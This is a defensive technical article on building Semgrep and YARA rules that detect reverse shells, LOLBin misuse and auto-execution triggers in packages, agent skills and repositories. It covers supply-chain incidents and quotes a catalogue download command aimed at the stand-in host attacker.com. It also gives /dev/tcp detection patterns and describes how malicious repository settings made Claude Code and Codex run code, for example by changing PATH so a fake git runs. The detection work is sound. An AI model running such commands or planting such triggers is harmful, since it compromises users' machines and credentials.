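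A scanner can use the trigger to find the payload. It can follow `dependsOn` to other tasks, look up an npm script in `package.json`, and open any local file the command runs, then apply the rest of the rule pack to what it finds, including the rules for reverse shells. A match on the payload would be a reason to stop the folder from opening. If the payload contains nothing suspicious, the scanner should still report the trigger, but as information for the reviewer rather than an alarm.

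VS Code's Workspace Trust prompt, which asks users whether they trust a folder, would remain as a second check if the user has kept it on. The chip maker NXP tells developers in *Important notes and limitations of MCUXpresso Tasks automation framework* to switch the feature off because it interferes with the company's tasks. Developers who do so have one less check between opening a folder and running its tasks.

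### Cases from 2025 and 2026

The clearest example of an attack through a `.pth` file involved LiteLLM, a Python package that connects programs to many language models. On March 24, 2026, attackers published two malicious versions on PyPI. LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) reports that version 1.82.7 had a payload in `proxy_server.py`, and that version 1.82.8 had the same kind of payload and also included `litellm_init.pth`. The malware collected passwords, cloud credentials and SSH keys and sent them to a domain that didn't belong to LiteLLM.

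Willison (2026), in *Malicious litellm_init.pth in litellm 1.82.8*, notes that the theft in 1.82.7 began only when a program imported the affected module, while installing 1.82.8 was enough to set it off. Its `.pth` file then ran whenever any Python program started on the machine, even if the program didn't use LiteLLM.

A rule for import lines in `.pth` files would have matched `litellm_init.pth`, since Python executes no other lines in such a file, but it would have found nothing in version 1.82.7. The file's size was also suspicious. Coopersmith (2026), in *litellm pypi packages compromised, infostealer added*, relays a report that it had 34,628 bytes, far more than a list of a few folders needs. A rule for the payload would have had less to match. HiddenLayer's *LiteLLM Supply Chain Attack* (2026) reports that the attackers had encoded the payload twice, which hides the names of the credentials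 from a text search.

Where and when the scan ran would have mattered as much as the rule. The attackers uploaded the packages directly to PyPI and left the GitHub repository untouched, so a scan of the public source code would have found nothing. PyPI quarantined the packages after about 40 minutes, so a scanner that checked new releases once a day could have missed them, whereas a check during installation would have had access to the file. Scanners also bring risks. LiteLLM believes the attackers got in through Trivy, a security scanner it ran in its release process.

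Two later attacks on Python packages contained less that a rule for declared triggers could match. In May 2026, attackers published malicious versions of more than 170 npm packages and two PyPI packages, including version 2.4.6 of mistralai, a package for using Mistral's models. Jensen, Dholakia and colleagues (2026) report that its malware ran when a program imported the package. There was therefore no key or special file to match, and detection depended on recognising the payload in ordinary source code. On October 21, 2026, LiteLLM's own release pipeline published version 1.107.0 with compiled malware, according to the same incident reports. Rules written for source code can't match compiled malware.

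Coding agents' settings have exposed users to risk even without a confirmed attack. CVE-2025-59536 is a publicly registered vulnerability in older versions of Claude Code. The field guide theorydelta reports that if a project had the setting `enableAllProjectMcpServers`, Claude Code started every server in `.mcp.json` before it showed the trust dialog. Anthropic fixed this in version 1.0.111. A rule for server entries in `.mcp.json` would have matched the trigger, and a rule for the setting would have identified the dangerous combination. Neither could have detected the fault itself, which was in Claude Code and not in the files it read. The same `.mcp.json` would be much less dangerous in a version that waited for approval.

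The security company Adversa AI later described an attack that runs only after the user accepts the trust dialog. A repository's settings can approve its own tool servers, so one click on "Yes, I trust this folder" starts them with all of the user's privileges. Here too, the trigger is in files that a rule can check before the user clicks. Project settings that approve the project's own servers are more suspicious than a server entry alone.

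A rule pack that covers only hooks, the best-known trigger, would miss an attack demonstrated by Datadog Security Labs. *Before the First Prompt* (Vaughan, 2026) dates the report to August 3, 2026. Codex had begun requiring users to review and approve hooks, so Datadog's researchers tested whether a malicious repository could run code automatically without one. In both Codex and Claude Code, once the user had trusted the folder, the repository's code ran before the first prompt, with no response from the model and no request to approve a shell command.

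In Codex, the trigger was a tool-server entry in `.codex/config.toml`. A rule for `mcp_servers` would have matched it, but would also match every legitimate project that configures a server. In Claude Code, `.claude/settings.json` changed PATH, the list of folders the system searches for programs, to put the repository's `bin` folder first. Claude Code calls Git automatically when it starts, so it ran the repository's file named `git` instead of the real program. Datadog Security Labs observed both results on a Mac, with Codex CLI 0.143.0 and Claude Code 2.1.185.

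A rule for hooks would have matched neither repository. To catch the Claude Code version, a rule has to look for project settings that change PATH, but some projects may do this to use their own copies of tools. The rule can exclude some of these projects by also checking whether the changed PATH leads to a folder in the repository that contains a file with the name of a common system program.

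## From public attack catalogues to rule packs

For auto-execution, a rule writer can start from the documentation of npm, VS Code or Claude Code, which lists the relevant files and keys. Reverse shells and the misuse of LOLBins have no such specification. The nearest substitute is an attack catalogue, a public list of techniques or commands that volunteers maintain for penetration testers and defenders. GTFOBins and LOLBAS both publish their entries as structured data, so a short program could turn every entry into a rule. Many of those rules would be useless, for reasons that vary with the entry's contents.

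### GTFOBins

GTFOBins keeps one YAML file per program. Each file lists the functions that the program can perform for an attacker, with at least one example command for each function. GTFOBins' *Scope* defines eleven functions, some more useful than others for scanning scripts.

| Function | What the program can do | Relevance to a scan of scripts |
|---|---|---|
| Reverse shell, bind shell | give someone on another machine a shell | high |
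| Download, upload | move data between machines | one step in many attacks and many ordinary scripts |
| Shell, command | start a shell or another command | high if an agent may run this program but not a shell |
| Library load | load a shared library, whose code then runs inside the program | the payload is in another file |
| File read, file write | read or change local files | low, since a script can do this anyway |
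| Privilege escalation | help a user gain more rights, for example by changing who owns another program | depends on the rights the program has |
| Inherit | open another listed program and gain its functions | the rule has to come from the other entry |

Each example also lists the contexts in which it works. In the "unprivileged" context, any user can run it. The others, sudo, SUID and capabilities, apply when a program has more rights than the person who starts it. Sudo runs a command as another user, usually the administrator. The SUID bit is a file setting that makes a program run with its owner's rights. Capabilities are individual privileges that Linux can grant to a program.

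The project also publishes all its entries in one JSON file. In the copy of April 29, 2026, 19 of the first 51 entries list file reading as their only function, and only three (ab, aria2c and Bash) directly list downloading, uploading or a remote shell. The entries are in alphabetical order, so the first 51 aren't a random sample, but many of them have little to do with reverse shells. A script gains nothing by reading a file with `base64` if it could read the same file with `cat`. Using `base64` is useful when it has administrator rights and the script doesn't. This fits GTFOBins's description of its subject as "misconfigured systems", by which it means machines whose local restrictions a listed program can bypass.

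Even where GTFOBins would make a poor source of rules for scripts, it can help a defender review the commands that an agent may run without asking, such as those in a skill's allowed-tools field. For example, GTFOBins lists "command" among the functions of aria2c, a download program, which means that an agent allowed to run aria2c can also start other programs through it.

Anyone who converts the JSON file automatically has to follow its cross-references, because some entries are only aliases and others inherit functions. The entry for `awk`, for example, points to `mawk` and has no command of its own. One example for Amazon's command-line tool is just `aws help`, which is listed because the help text opens in `less`, a text viewer with functions of its own. A rule copied from this example would flag ordinary requests for help. The shell example for Bash is the single word `bash`, and a rule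 made from it would match a large share of all shell scripts.

### LOLBAS and its detection links

LOLBAS's *Living Off The Land Binaries and Scripts (and now also Libraries)* has narrower entry criteria. A file must be signed by Microsoft and either come with Windows or be a download from Microsoft. It must do something "unexpected" beyond its intended use, although the project exempts ways around application allowlists, which restrict the programs a machine may run. It must also be useful to an APT (a well-resourced group of attackers) or to a red team, which tests an organisation's defences by attacking them. Accepted functions include running code, transferring files, stealing credentials and altering logs.

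The requirement of unexpected behaviour affects how strong the evidence from a match is. The GTFOBins download entry for aria2c describes the tool's normal job, which is downloading files. Certutil.exe is meant for handling certificates, so a match on a script that fetches a program with it is stronger evidence than a match on aria2c, though an administrator may still have an innocent reason for using it that way.

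For each command, LOLBAS records its use, category, required privileges, supported Windows versions and MITRE ATT&CK technique number. Placeholders such as `{REMOTEURL:.exe}` mark many of the variable parts. Three of the seven commands in the certutil entry are in the download category. Each uses a different option, so a rule copied from one would miss the other two.

Entries also link to existing detection rules, which GTFOBins entries don't. The certutil entry links to eight rules, three in Sigma (a format for log searches that people can translate for different monitoring products), two from Elastic and three from Splunk. Coverage is uneven, and the entry for Change.exe, which dates from July 2025, has no linked rule, only a sentence about what to look for.

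Most of the linked rules examine running programs, and only some of their conditions can be checked in source code. A static rule can look for a command-line option that a linked rule checks for, but it can't reproduce a Sigma rule that looks for uncommon child processes of AddinUtil.exe, because a script's text doesn't show which processes AddinUtil.exe will start. Many of the Sigma links lead to a fixed revision of the rule, so a reader may find an outdated version.

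### Collections of payloads and arguments

Payload collections have less structure than catalogues. PayloadsAllTheThings, a repository of attack strings for penetration testers, groups them by type of attack, and detection rules cite it. A collection can offer several spellings of a technique where a catalogue has a single example. But it has no standard fields for functions or required privileges, so a rule writer has to work out which parts of each string matter. Copying whole strings produces narrow rules like Roth's Awk entry, which depends on a variable name.

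GTFOArgs is a catalogue of program arguments, maintained by Joshua Rogers and modelled on GTFOBins. It lists 26 programs, including `git`, `tar`, `find` and `curl`, with the legitimate arguments that let someone break out of a restricted environment. This helps in deciding which flags a rule should require, a decision that comes up in every conversion.

### Converting one entry

The GTFOBins entry for aria2c gives this example of a download:

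```
aria2c -o /path/to/ouput-file http://attacker.com/path/to/input-file
```

The first step is to replace the variable parts with placeholders. GTFOBins asks contributors to use standard values, such as `attacker.com` for the attacker's machine and `12345` for a port, so a converter can search for them. It would miss one here, because the entry has "ouput-file" instead of the standard "output-file". A rule that kept the misspelt path would match only scripts that contain the example unchanged.

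Next, the rule writer decides which flags are essential. According to the entry's comment, `-o` is optional because without it, aria2c saves the file under its original name in the current folder. Dropping it leaves two parts of the example.

| In the example | Decision | In the rule |
|---|---|---|
| `aria2c` | required | `\baria2c\b` |
| `-o` and the output path | optional | `[^\n]*`, any text on the same line |
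| the address at attacker.com | any web address | `https?://\S+` |

aria2c can also start a second program when a download finishes or fails, but only if the command includes an option that begins with `--on-download-`. A rule to detect this should require that option, and it could have a higher severity than a rule for downloads because it involves running another program.

The rule also needs a list of file types. Shell scripts are the obvious choice, but Markdown and JSON belong on the list too because of SKILL.md and `package.json`. In Semgrep's format, the result is:

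```
rules:
  - id: aria2c-download
    languages: [regex]
    severity: INFO
    message: This command downloads a file with aria2c.
    paths:
      include: ["*.sh", "*.md", "*.json"]
    pattern-regex: \baria2c\b[^\n]*\bhttps?://\S+
```

Finally, the rule needs tests. Semgrep reads the expected result from a comment above each line, where `ruleid` means the rule must match and `ok` means it must not.

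```
# ruleid: aria2c-download
aria2c https://example.com/report.csv

# ok: aria2c-download
aria2c --version
```

The first test leaves out `-o`, so a rule that wrongly requires the flag would fail it. The second contains the program's name but no download, so a rule that matches only the name would fail it.

Even a rule that passes both tests gives some wrong results. This one matches a Markdown sentence that mentions `aria2c` and links to its manual. It misses `aria2c "$REPORT_URL"` because an earlier line sets the address, and it misses a VS Code task that puts the program and the address on separate lines. Rule writers usually find such cases by running the rule on many real files, then add them to the tests.

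### What the entry leaves out

Even an accurate match would show only that a command downloads a file, and scripts that fetch datasets or software updates contain the same command. A GTFOBins entry records a way an attacker can use a program, but it has no field that distinguishes this from ordinary use. The example's `attacker.com` marks the address as hostile, but the converter replaces it with a pattern that matches any address. The rule above therefore has the severity INFO, and its message describes the command without calling it an attack.

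Conversion can also lose the context. The entry for agetty, which handles logins on a terminal, has one example, and its only context is SUID. A rule made from it would report a risk that exists only on machines where someone has set the SUID bit on agetty, which a scanner can't determine from a skill's files. Dropping every example that lacks the "unprivileged" context would remove agetty but keep all the ways to read a file that the user can read anyway, so someone still has to choose which functions deserve rules. A command in a script that sets the SUID bit on a program is a better target for a rule, because it creates the misconfiguration and appears in the files being scanned.

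An example also shows only one spelling of a technique. For Change.exe, LOLBAS gives a command that ends in `user`, and the description lists `port` and `logon` as alternatives. A converter that reads only the command field would miss both. A person can sometimes find other spellings in the description or the program's manual, as with aria2c's optional flag, but an entry may not list them all.

### Where existing packs get their patterns

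At least one rule pack comes directly from a catalogue, but it applies to logs rather than source code. It is a set of Sigma rules that detect GTFOBins commands on Linux, and it appears in GitHub's list of projects related to GTFOBins. The rules in the better-known scanners for packages and skills have other documented origins, or none.

The monitoring company Datadog released GuardDog in November 2022 to find malicious packages on PyPI. Datadog wrote GuardDog's first source-code rules in Semgrep's format to capture patterns it had observed in attacks. But *Introducing GuardDog 3.0* (2026) acknowledges that the rules "overfit specific examples of malicious code", which made new malware harder to identify. Semgrep was also slow on packages with many files and needed a lot of memory for large ones. Datadog therefore moved the rules to YARA.

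Some GuardDog rules now identify a capability, such as making network calls, and others identify a threat indicator, such as a suspicious domain or the name of a sensitive file. This change is more relevant to overfitting than the new engine, which can't prevent it by itself because a YARA rule can be just as narrow. GuardDog reports a high risk only when a capability and an indicator appear in the same file, and it lowers the severity if they are in different files. Under this scheme, the aria2c rule would be a capability rule, and a match would need other evidence before anyone treated the package as hostile.

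The documentation for version 3.2.0 of Datadog's *GuardDog* lists five research papers as inspiration, most of them about attacks on package registries. GuardDog bases its attack stages on MITRE ATT&CK, and the documentation mentions neither GTFOBins nor LOLBAS. The meaning of a score can change between versions. In June 2026, Datadog described a score of 7.2 out of 10 as high risk and likely malicious, but by version 3.2.0, released that August, the same score meant medium risk. A team that blocks packages above a fixed score therefore has to check the threshold after each update.

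GuardDog's defaults suit packages better than skills. By default, its YARA rules skip Markdown, JSON, YAML and TOML files. This reduces noise from documentation and data, but in a skill or a cloned repository it also excludes SKILL.md, `.vscode/tasks.json`, `.mcp.json` and `.codex/config.toml`, which can contain commands or triggers. Datadog did add a rule to an early version of GuardDog for one trigger in a JSON file, npm installation scripts.

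NVIDIA's *SkillSpector* scans skills. In May 2026 its documentation listed 64 patterns in 16 categories, from instructions that override safety constraints to dangerous function calls. It combines regular expressions, syntax-tree checks, data-flow tracking and YARA signatures, and an optional language model reviews the findings. NVIDIA bases the tool on *Agent Skills in the Wild*, the study by Liu, Wang and colleagues, and doesn't credit any catalogue of commands.

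None of the 64 descriptions mentions reverse shells. A Python reverse shell would probably match the pattern for `subprocess` calls, but so would any script that starts another program. SkillSpector also has a "critical" pattern for network input that flows into such a call. But in a Python reverse shell built on `os.dup2`, no variable carries the attacker's commands to the call, so a rule that tracks variables may find no flow. The YARA signatures for malware and hacking tools might catch some reverse shells. For auto-execution, one pattern covers scheduled jobs and startup scripts, but no description mentions agent hooks or editor tasks.

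The pack has since grown to 68 patterns in 17 categories, by NVIDIA's count. Socket, a company that checks open-source packages, has a newer copy of the documentation on its *skillspector* page. Three of the four additions listed there cover instructions meant to stop an agent from refusing requests or giving warnings, and the fourth covers indirect calls that two older rules miss. The page also warns that Socket detected malware in the PyPI package called skillspector. The package could be an impostor, or the scanner signatures it contains could have set off a false alarm. NVIDIA tells users to install the tool from its GitHub repository, which is the safer source in either case.

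Cisco's Skill Scanner uses three types of rule: regular expressions in YAML files, YARA rules and checks written in Python. Cisco's description of them gives no source for the built-in patterns. Users can add their own rules, so a team could translate rules derived from GTFOBins into a supported format and load them. An early version of the scanner applied text patterns to all files but data-flow analysis only to Python, so it would have checked the sales-report skill's `build.js` only with text patterns.

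Microsoft's OSS-Detect-Backdoor looks for backdoors in open-source packages and runs its rules on an engine called Application Inspector. Microsoft presents the engine as a way to find out what a program does, with hundreds of rules for features such as file operations, encryption and shell commands. GTFOBins lists commands typed into a shell, but these rules rely on well-known library and API calls, so they work on source code that never calls a program listed in GTFOBins.

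The rules in the public Semgrep registry come from many contributors and have no single origin. Its reverse-shell rules for Python and Java are probably based on how such programs are written in each language, since no shell command from a catalogue would supply the calls that those rules match.

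## How a Semgrep rule matches a script

A Semgrep pattern usually looks like ordinary code with some parts left open. If Semgrep has a parser for the language, it compares the pattern's structure with the script's. The aria2c rule declared `regex` as its language, so Semgrep skipped this step and searched the script as plain text.

### From rule to finding

The following rule looks for one of the triggers for auto-execution, a Python call that loads pickle data:

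```
rules:
  - id: pickle-load
    languages: [python]
    severity: INFO
    message: This call loads $FILE and can run code stored in it.
    pattern: pickle.load($FILE)
```

Suppose the sales-report skill also has a Python script with these lines:

```
import pickle

# pickle.load(old_totals)
totals = pickle.load(
    open("totals.pkl", "rb")
)
```

Semgrep reads the YAML and uses the `languages` line to choose which files to check against the rule and which parser to use. The parser turns both the script and the pattern into syntax trees. Semgrep then searches the script's tree for a part with the same structure as the pattern. It finds the call that starts on line 4, where the metavariable `$FILE` matches `open("totals.pkl", "rb")`. The line breaks inside the call don't affect the match, and the call on line 3 doesn't match because it is a comment.

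Semgrep then applies any further conditions in the rule and drops every match that fails one. It reports each remaining match with the file, the line and the rule's message, replacing `$FILE` in the message with the captured code.

Opengrep works the same way. Several security companies started it as a fork (an independent continuation) of Semgrep's open-source code. The introductory example in its documentation runs one rule on one file and reports one finding. Opengrep can also write the finding as structured data, with the exact start and end of the match, for another program to read. In March, Semgrep (2026) released a plugin that automatically scans every file in the coding agents Claude Code and Cursor.

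A file that the scanner skipped produces no findings, just like a harmless one, so the number of files in the summary is worth checking. Opengrep's example scans only files that Git tracks, so a similar scan could miss a skill that someone has just copied into a repository. Parsing can also fail without a warning. Semgrep's *Releases* (2024) records a fix for a silent parsing error in Dockerfiles (instructions for building containers) that didn't end with a newline character. Before March 2026, Semgrep also ignored errors in locating the files to scan, which it now reports as warnings.

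### Combining patterns

Most rules for reverse shells need more than one pattern. These are the main operators:

| Operator | Effect |
|---|---|
| `$X` (metavariable) | stands for one piece of code and captures it; if the name appears twice, both places must contain the same code |
| `...` (ellipsis) | stands for any number of arguments, statements or other items, including none |
| `patterns` | requires every condition in a list |
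| `pattern-either` | requires at least one pattern in a list |
| `pattern-inside` | keeps a match only if it lies within code that fits a second pattern |
| `pattern-not` | drops a match that also fits a second pattern |
| `metavariable-regex` | requires the captured code to match a regular expression |

A rule can use `pattern-not` to find code that lacks something. In *35 more Semgrep rules*, the security consultancy Trail of Bits includes a rule for settings that let automated GitHub jobs use an Amazon cloud account. The rule uses `pattern-inside` to find the relevant part of the settings, then `pattern-not` to exclude those that restrict which repository may use the account. It reports the rest, which any repository on GitHub could exploit.

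A regular expression can also exclude values. Trail of Bits' *30 new Semgrep rules* includes a rule for Docker Compose, a format for configuring groups of containers. The rule captures each network port in `$PORT` and skips those that begin with an address of the machine itself, such as 127.0.0.1. A reverse-shell rule could exclude local connections in the same way, as Elastic's terminal rule does.

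In taint mode, Semgrep tracks how data flows through a program. A taint rule lists sources, where a value enters the program, and sinks, where it could do harm. It can also list sanitizers, which make the value safe. Semgrep reports a sink if a value from a source can reach it without passing through a sanitizer. For build.js, the source would be the environment variable that holds the secret key, and the sink would be the network request.

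Semgrep's free Community Edition analyses one function at a time, while the commercial product, Semgrep Code, can follow JavaScript and Python values between files, according to Semgrep's list of supported languages. If build.js read the key in one function and sent it from another, a taint rule in the Community Edition would probably miss the leak. Opengrep has added taint analysis across functions, according to Aikido, one of its founding companies.

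### The Python rule, line by line

The April 2024 version of the Semgrep registry's *python-reverse-shell* rule has two alternative calls, a condition on the path of the program the call starts, and three lines of surrounding code.

| Part of the rule | What it requires |
|---|---|
| `pty.spawn("$BINPATH",...)` | a call that starts a program in a simulated terminal |
| `subprocess.call(["$BINPATH",...],...)` | or a call that starts a program from a list, with the program's path as the first item |
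| `/bin/.*?sh\b` | a path with `/bin/`, then any characters, then `sh` at the end of a word |
| `import socket` | Python's module for network connections |
| `$S = socket.socket(...)` | a new socket, stored in a variable |
| `$S.connect(($IP,$PORT),...)` | a connection through the same variable |

The two calls are under `pattern-either`, so matching either one is enough. The regular expression is a `metavariable-regex` condition on `$BINPATH`. The last three lines form a single `pattern-inside`, with an ellipsis after each line to allow for other code.

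The regular expression matches the usual shells, such as `/bin/sh`, `/bin/bash` and `/bin/zsh`. It also matches `/bin/ssh`, which opens a shell on another machine, and `/bin/backup.sh`, which would be somebody's own script. It doesn't match plain `bash` because it lacks `/bin/`.

The three surrounding lines show that the program connects to something, but they don't connect the shell to the socket. The following harmless script therefore meets every condition:

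```
import socket
import subprocess

db = socket.socket()
db.connect(("db.example.com", 5432))
db.close()
subprocess.call(["/bin/sh", "migrate.sh"])
```

The script checks that a database is reachable, closes the connection and runs a local update script in a shell. Nobody on the network can type into that shell, but the rule would still report "a Python reverse shell" and list `/bin/sh`, the database server and port 5432.

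The rule would also match a script that ran the update before contacting the database. The code that fits `pattern-inside` begins at the import, so it includes any shell call between the import and the connection.

In the rule's metadata, Semgrep gives it low confidence, low likelihood and medium impact, and files it under "audit", but the rule's message is worded more strongly. A team that shows reviewers only the message should add the confidence level. The rule's category, which comes from a public list of software weaknesses called CWE, is also misleading because it refers to a command shell in an externally accessible directory rather than a program that connects out.

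The rule comes with three tests, all reverse shells that it must match. They include both of the listed calls and import several modules in one statement. Semgrep parses that statement, so it recognises `import socket` even when another module's name comes first. One test takes the address and port from environment variables. It still matches because `$IP` and `$PORT` can stand for any expression, but the message then contains the code that looks up the address instead of the address itself.

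All three tests also attach the standard streams to the socket with `os.dup2`, although the rule doesn't check for this. No test is marked `ok`, so the tests can't reveal a false positive such as the database script. Requiring `os.dup2` would exclude that script, but the rule would then miss any reverse shell that attaches the streams another way.

The rule misses several classes of programs that do the same thing as the ones it matches. The largest class uses other library functions for the same steps, since Python has many ways to start a process and more than one way to open a connection. Another class computes the shell's path at run time, so the regular expression has no path to check. Semgrep can sometimes determine that an expression produces a fixed string without identifying the string, as Semgrep's *Releases* (2023) explains for Java. The rule also misses programs split between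 two files.

A program that reads commands from the network and launches them itself, like the one Pellitteri and Susini describe, doesn't name a shell, so taint mode suits this case better. The source would be data received from a socket, and the sinks would be functions that start a program. Such a rule would miss the three tests above, which rely on `os.dup2`, so a rule pack needs both kinds of rule.

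### The Java rule and its model

Semgrep's *java-reverse-shell* rule is much narrower. Its only test is a program from PayloadsAllTheThings, and the pattern follows that program almost statement by statement.

The rule's `pattern-inside` requires code that uses `ProcessBuilder` to start a process, with its error messages merged into its normal output, and later destroys that process. Between those two steps, the code must create a socket, get its input stream and start a loop that runs until the socket closes. Inside that loop, a second loop must copy data from the socket one byte at a time while any is available. A `flush` call, which sends any waiting data, must follow.

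A harmless program is unlikely to contain all of this by accident. The loop is also direct evidence that the program passes on data from the network, and the Python rule requires no such evidence. But the rule doesn't require code that sends the shell's output back, because an ellipsis covers that part of the model program. It also doesn't check that the incoming data goes to the process. The metavariable for the destination, `$PO`, appears only once, so it could stand for a file.

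The rule doesn't specify a shell either. It accepts any arguments to `ProcessBuilder`, so a legitimate program that forwards network data to a local tool could match if it used the same loop. Semgrep's message for this rule, "potential reverse shell behavior", reflects that uncertainty better than the Python rule's message does.

The rule's main weakness is recall. A Java program that copies data in blocks, uses a separate thread for each direction, or never destroys the process does the same thing with a different structure. If someone copies the program the rule is based on and renames its variables, the rule still matches, because metavariables stand for the names. A text search for the whole program would miss that copy. But the rule will probably miss a reverse shell that someone wrote from scratch.

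### Searching text instead

Both rules need code that parses as one language. An agent skill's SKILL.md file can mix English, shell commands and Python, and the same command can also appear in a JSON file. Semgrep can search such files as text in two ways.

Semgrep's generic mode splits a file into words, punctuation and other bytes, and uses indentation to infer which lines belong together. Metavariables, ellipses and operators such as `pattern-inside` still work, but generic mode doesn't recognise comments, strings or function calls.

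Trail of Bits compared Semgrep's Python and generic modes on a short Python file. The file contains a call to `os.system`, which runs a command, and an earlier call that is commented out. The pattern `os.system(...)` produced one finding in Python mode and two in generic mode, which also reported the comment. Trail of Bits calls generic mode "glorified text search" and warns that it produces more false positives.

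Trail of Bits nevertheless used generic mode for 11 of the 30 rules in that release. One of them finds SSH commands that disable verification of the other machine's identity. Semgrep can parse Bash and Dockerfiles, but a Bash rule would find the command only in Bash scripts. The generic rule also finds it in Dockerfiles, build configuration, documentation and the system calls of other languages. Trail of Bits accepts some extra findings to avoid missing a critical bug, and suggests limiting a rule to certain file paths to reduce them.

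The same argument applies to skills, where the agent may run a command that appears in the documentation. Generic mode can't distinguish such a command from a commented-out call in a script, but the finding includes the file name, which a reviewer can use to tell them apart.

Generic mode also lacks equivalences, which let Semgrep match different spellings of the same code in a language it can parse. In Python mode, the pattern `import socket` also matches `import os, socket`. In generic mode, the pattern would miss that statement because `socket` must come directly after `import`.

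The ellipsis is also more limited in generic mode, where it can skip at most ten lines, so a pattern for a long function call may not reach the closing bracket. Semgrep's documentation recommends writing two or three ellipses in a row to cover 20 or 30 lines. Generic mode has an option to ignore comments in a given style, such as C's. According to the documentation, it is still possible, "or even easy", to write code that generic mode fails to match.

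The second way is a regular expression, as in the aria2c rule. Trail of Bits recommends this if the text usually fits on one line, occurs in many kinds of file and requires specific characters. Its example is a setting in database addresses that turns off encryption. The expression requires a `?` or `&` before the setting's name, which makes it likely that the match is part of an address. Generic mode has no easy way to express a choice between characters, but it works better for commands that span several lines.

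### An address is several words

In generic mode, a metavariable captures one word made of letters, digits and underscores. An IP address such as 192.0.2.10 is seven tokens in this mode (four numbers and three full stops), so a rule cannot capture the remote IP address of a connection with a single metavariable.

The table shows how three patterns for Bash's network path work on three pieces of text, assuming each match must stay on one line.

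| Pattern | `/dev/tcp/localhost/5432` | `/dev/tcp/192.0.2.10/443` | `/dev/tcp/$host/$port` |
|---|---|---|---|
| `/dev/tcp/$HOST/$PORT` | match | no match | no match |
| `/dev/tcp/$...HOST/$PORT` | match | match | no match |
| `/dev/tcp/$...TARGET` | match | match | match |

The first pattern matches a connection to the machine itself but misses one to an outside address. This is nearly the opposite of what a defender wants, even though the pattern looks right. It misses the second text because `$HOST` captures `192`, and the pattern then requires a slash where the text has a full stop.

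The second pattern uses an ellipsis metavariable, `$...HOST`, which captures a sequence of tokens and so matches the whole IP address. It does not match the third text because a shell variable such as `$port` is also more than one token, a dollar sign and a word.

By default, however, an ellipsis metavariable can continue for up to ten lines. Suppose a SKILL.md file contains these two lines:

```
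Bash treats /dev/tcp/ as a network path.
See docs/network.md for details.
```

The second pattern would match across both. It would capture everything between `/dev/tcp/` and the slash in `docs/network.md` as the host, and `network` as the port. The option `generic_ellipsis_max_span: 0` prevents this by keeping the ellipsis on one line:

```
rules:
  - id: bash-network-path
    languages: [generic]
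    severity: INFO
    message: This line has a Bash network path to $...HOST.
    options:
      generic_ellipsis_max_span: 0
    pattern: /dev/tcp/$...HOST/$PORT
```

With this option, the two lines of documentation no longer match because the first line has no further slash. The third pattern would still match that line because it accepts any text after `/dev/tcp/`. A rule writer has to decide whether finding paths with variable ports is worth the extra findings from documentation.

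Semgrep also offers an experimental engine for generic mode, called Aliengrep, which lets a rule treat additional characters as part of a word. If the rule adds the full stop, a plain metavariable can capture an IP address or a domain name. Aliengrep also has a setting to ignore case, which would help with Windows commands, since Windows accepts both `certutil` and `CertUtil`. Semgrep warns that Aliengrep's features may change.

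A regular expression may be the simplest choice for this path because the text fits on one line, has a fixed set of characters, and occurs in both scripts and documentation. The expression `/dev/tcp/[^/\s]+/\S+` matches all three texts in the table but neither line of the SKILL.md example.

### Bash and its redirections

Shell scripts are the most important case for reverse shells, but Semgrep supports them less well than it supports Python or Java. Semgrep (2021) added experimental support for Bash in version 0.71.0. Jambon (2021) reported in *Scanning Shell Scripts With Semgrep* that Semgrep could parse about 92% of shell code.

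Semgrep's Bash patterns could mostly match simple commands, pipelines, variables, loops and function definitions. This is enough for a rule that detects a script that downloads another script and pipes it into a shell. But Semgrep could not yet match file redirections, which many short shell commands for remote access depend on. In a Bash reverse shell, the `/dev/tcp` path is often the target of a redirection. In that case, a Bash pattern could find the shell command but not the network connection or the link between them.

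Semgrep also couldn't match background jobs, which let a script continue while a command runs, and it didn't interpret the options of common commands. Jambon gives the example of `set -eu` and `set -u -e`, which have the same effect but which Semgrep didn't treat as equivalent. A Bash pattern for `rm -rf` would therefore have had the same weakness as the text search in Anthropic's example hook.

In Bash patterns, shell variables and metavariables both begin with a dollar sign. Semgrep treats `$URL`, in capitals, as a metavariable that matches any expression, so a rule must use `${URL}` to match the shell variable of that name. A rule writer who copies a line from a malicious script into a pattern may therefore create a much broader rule than intended.

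Semgrep has improved its Bash support since then. Version 0.101.0 (2022) added support for commands in parentheses. But Semgrep still classed Bash as experimental in the August 2026 version of its language list. For experimental languages, it promises to parse at least 90% of code and to support ellipses and "basic metavariable functionality". The target parse rate for Python and Java in Semgrep Code is 99%.

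A good rule for reverse shells that use a named pipe would check that two commands use the same pipe, which requires a repeated metavariable to match the same text each time. Semgrep lists this feature only at the next level, beta, and above. It may work in Bash anyway, since one of Jambon's 2021 examples reuses a captured variable name, but a rule that relies on it needs a test.

It is also unclear whether Semgrep scans shell scripts that have no file extension and identify their interpreter on the first line, as many do. According to the November 2021 release notes, Semgrep would scan such scripts if they were executable, but a month later Jambon's post listed Bash scripts without an extension as unsupported. Even if the release notes are correct, Semgrep could miss a script that isn't marked executable, which an agent can still run by passing it to `bash`.

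Redirections do not appear in the current language list or the March 2026 release notes, so it is unclear whether Bash patterns can now match them. The March notes also list new beta support for PowerShell in Semgrep Code, which is one support level above Bash in that product.

Opengrep doesn't clearly solve the problem. Its documentation of November 2025 lists Bash among more than 30 languages but doesn't give the level of support for each. In an account of the project's first year, Aikido lists Visual Basic, Apex and Elixir as added languages and says Opengrep remains fully compatible with existing rules. *Semgrep to Opengrep migration* (2026) supports this claim, since Codacy, a code-checking service, kept all its patterns when it switched engines. But compatibility doesn't make redirections easier to match, and Opengrep probably inherited Semgrep's limits in Bash along with its code.

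For now, a rule pack can use Bash patterns for commands and pipelines, and text patterns for redirections. The text patterns have to allow for different spellings of the same redirection. According to GNU's Bash manual, `<` refers to stream 0 and `>` to stream 1 if the script gives no number, so `>` and `1>` mean the same thing. The order of redirections also matters, according to the manual, so a rule can't treat every arrangement of the same symbols as equivalent.

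A team can check its own version of either scanner with a harmless test. The rule would have the language `bash`, the id `echo-to-file` and the pattern `echo ... > $FILE`, and the test file would contain two commands:

```
# ruleid: echo-to-file
echo ready > status.txt

# ok: echo-to-file
echo ready
```

If the scanner misses the first command, it can't match this redirection. If it reports the second, it ignored the redirection in the pattern, and a reverse-shell rule written the same way could flag ordinary shell commands.

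## Running the rules on snippets

A Semgrep rule for Python or Bash is designed for a complete file in one language, but agents often handle only fragments. For example, when Claude Code is about to run a command, a checking script receives the command but not the code around it. The table lists common kinds of snippet.

| Snippet | Where it comes from | What is missing |
|---|---|---|
| Command in a tool call | the agent writes it for the shell | earlier commands and the contents of any script it runs |
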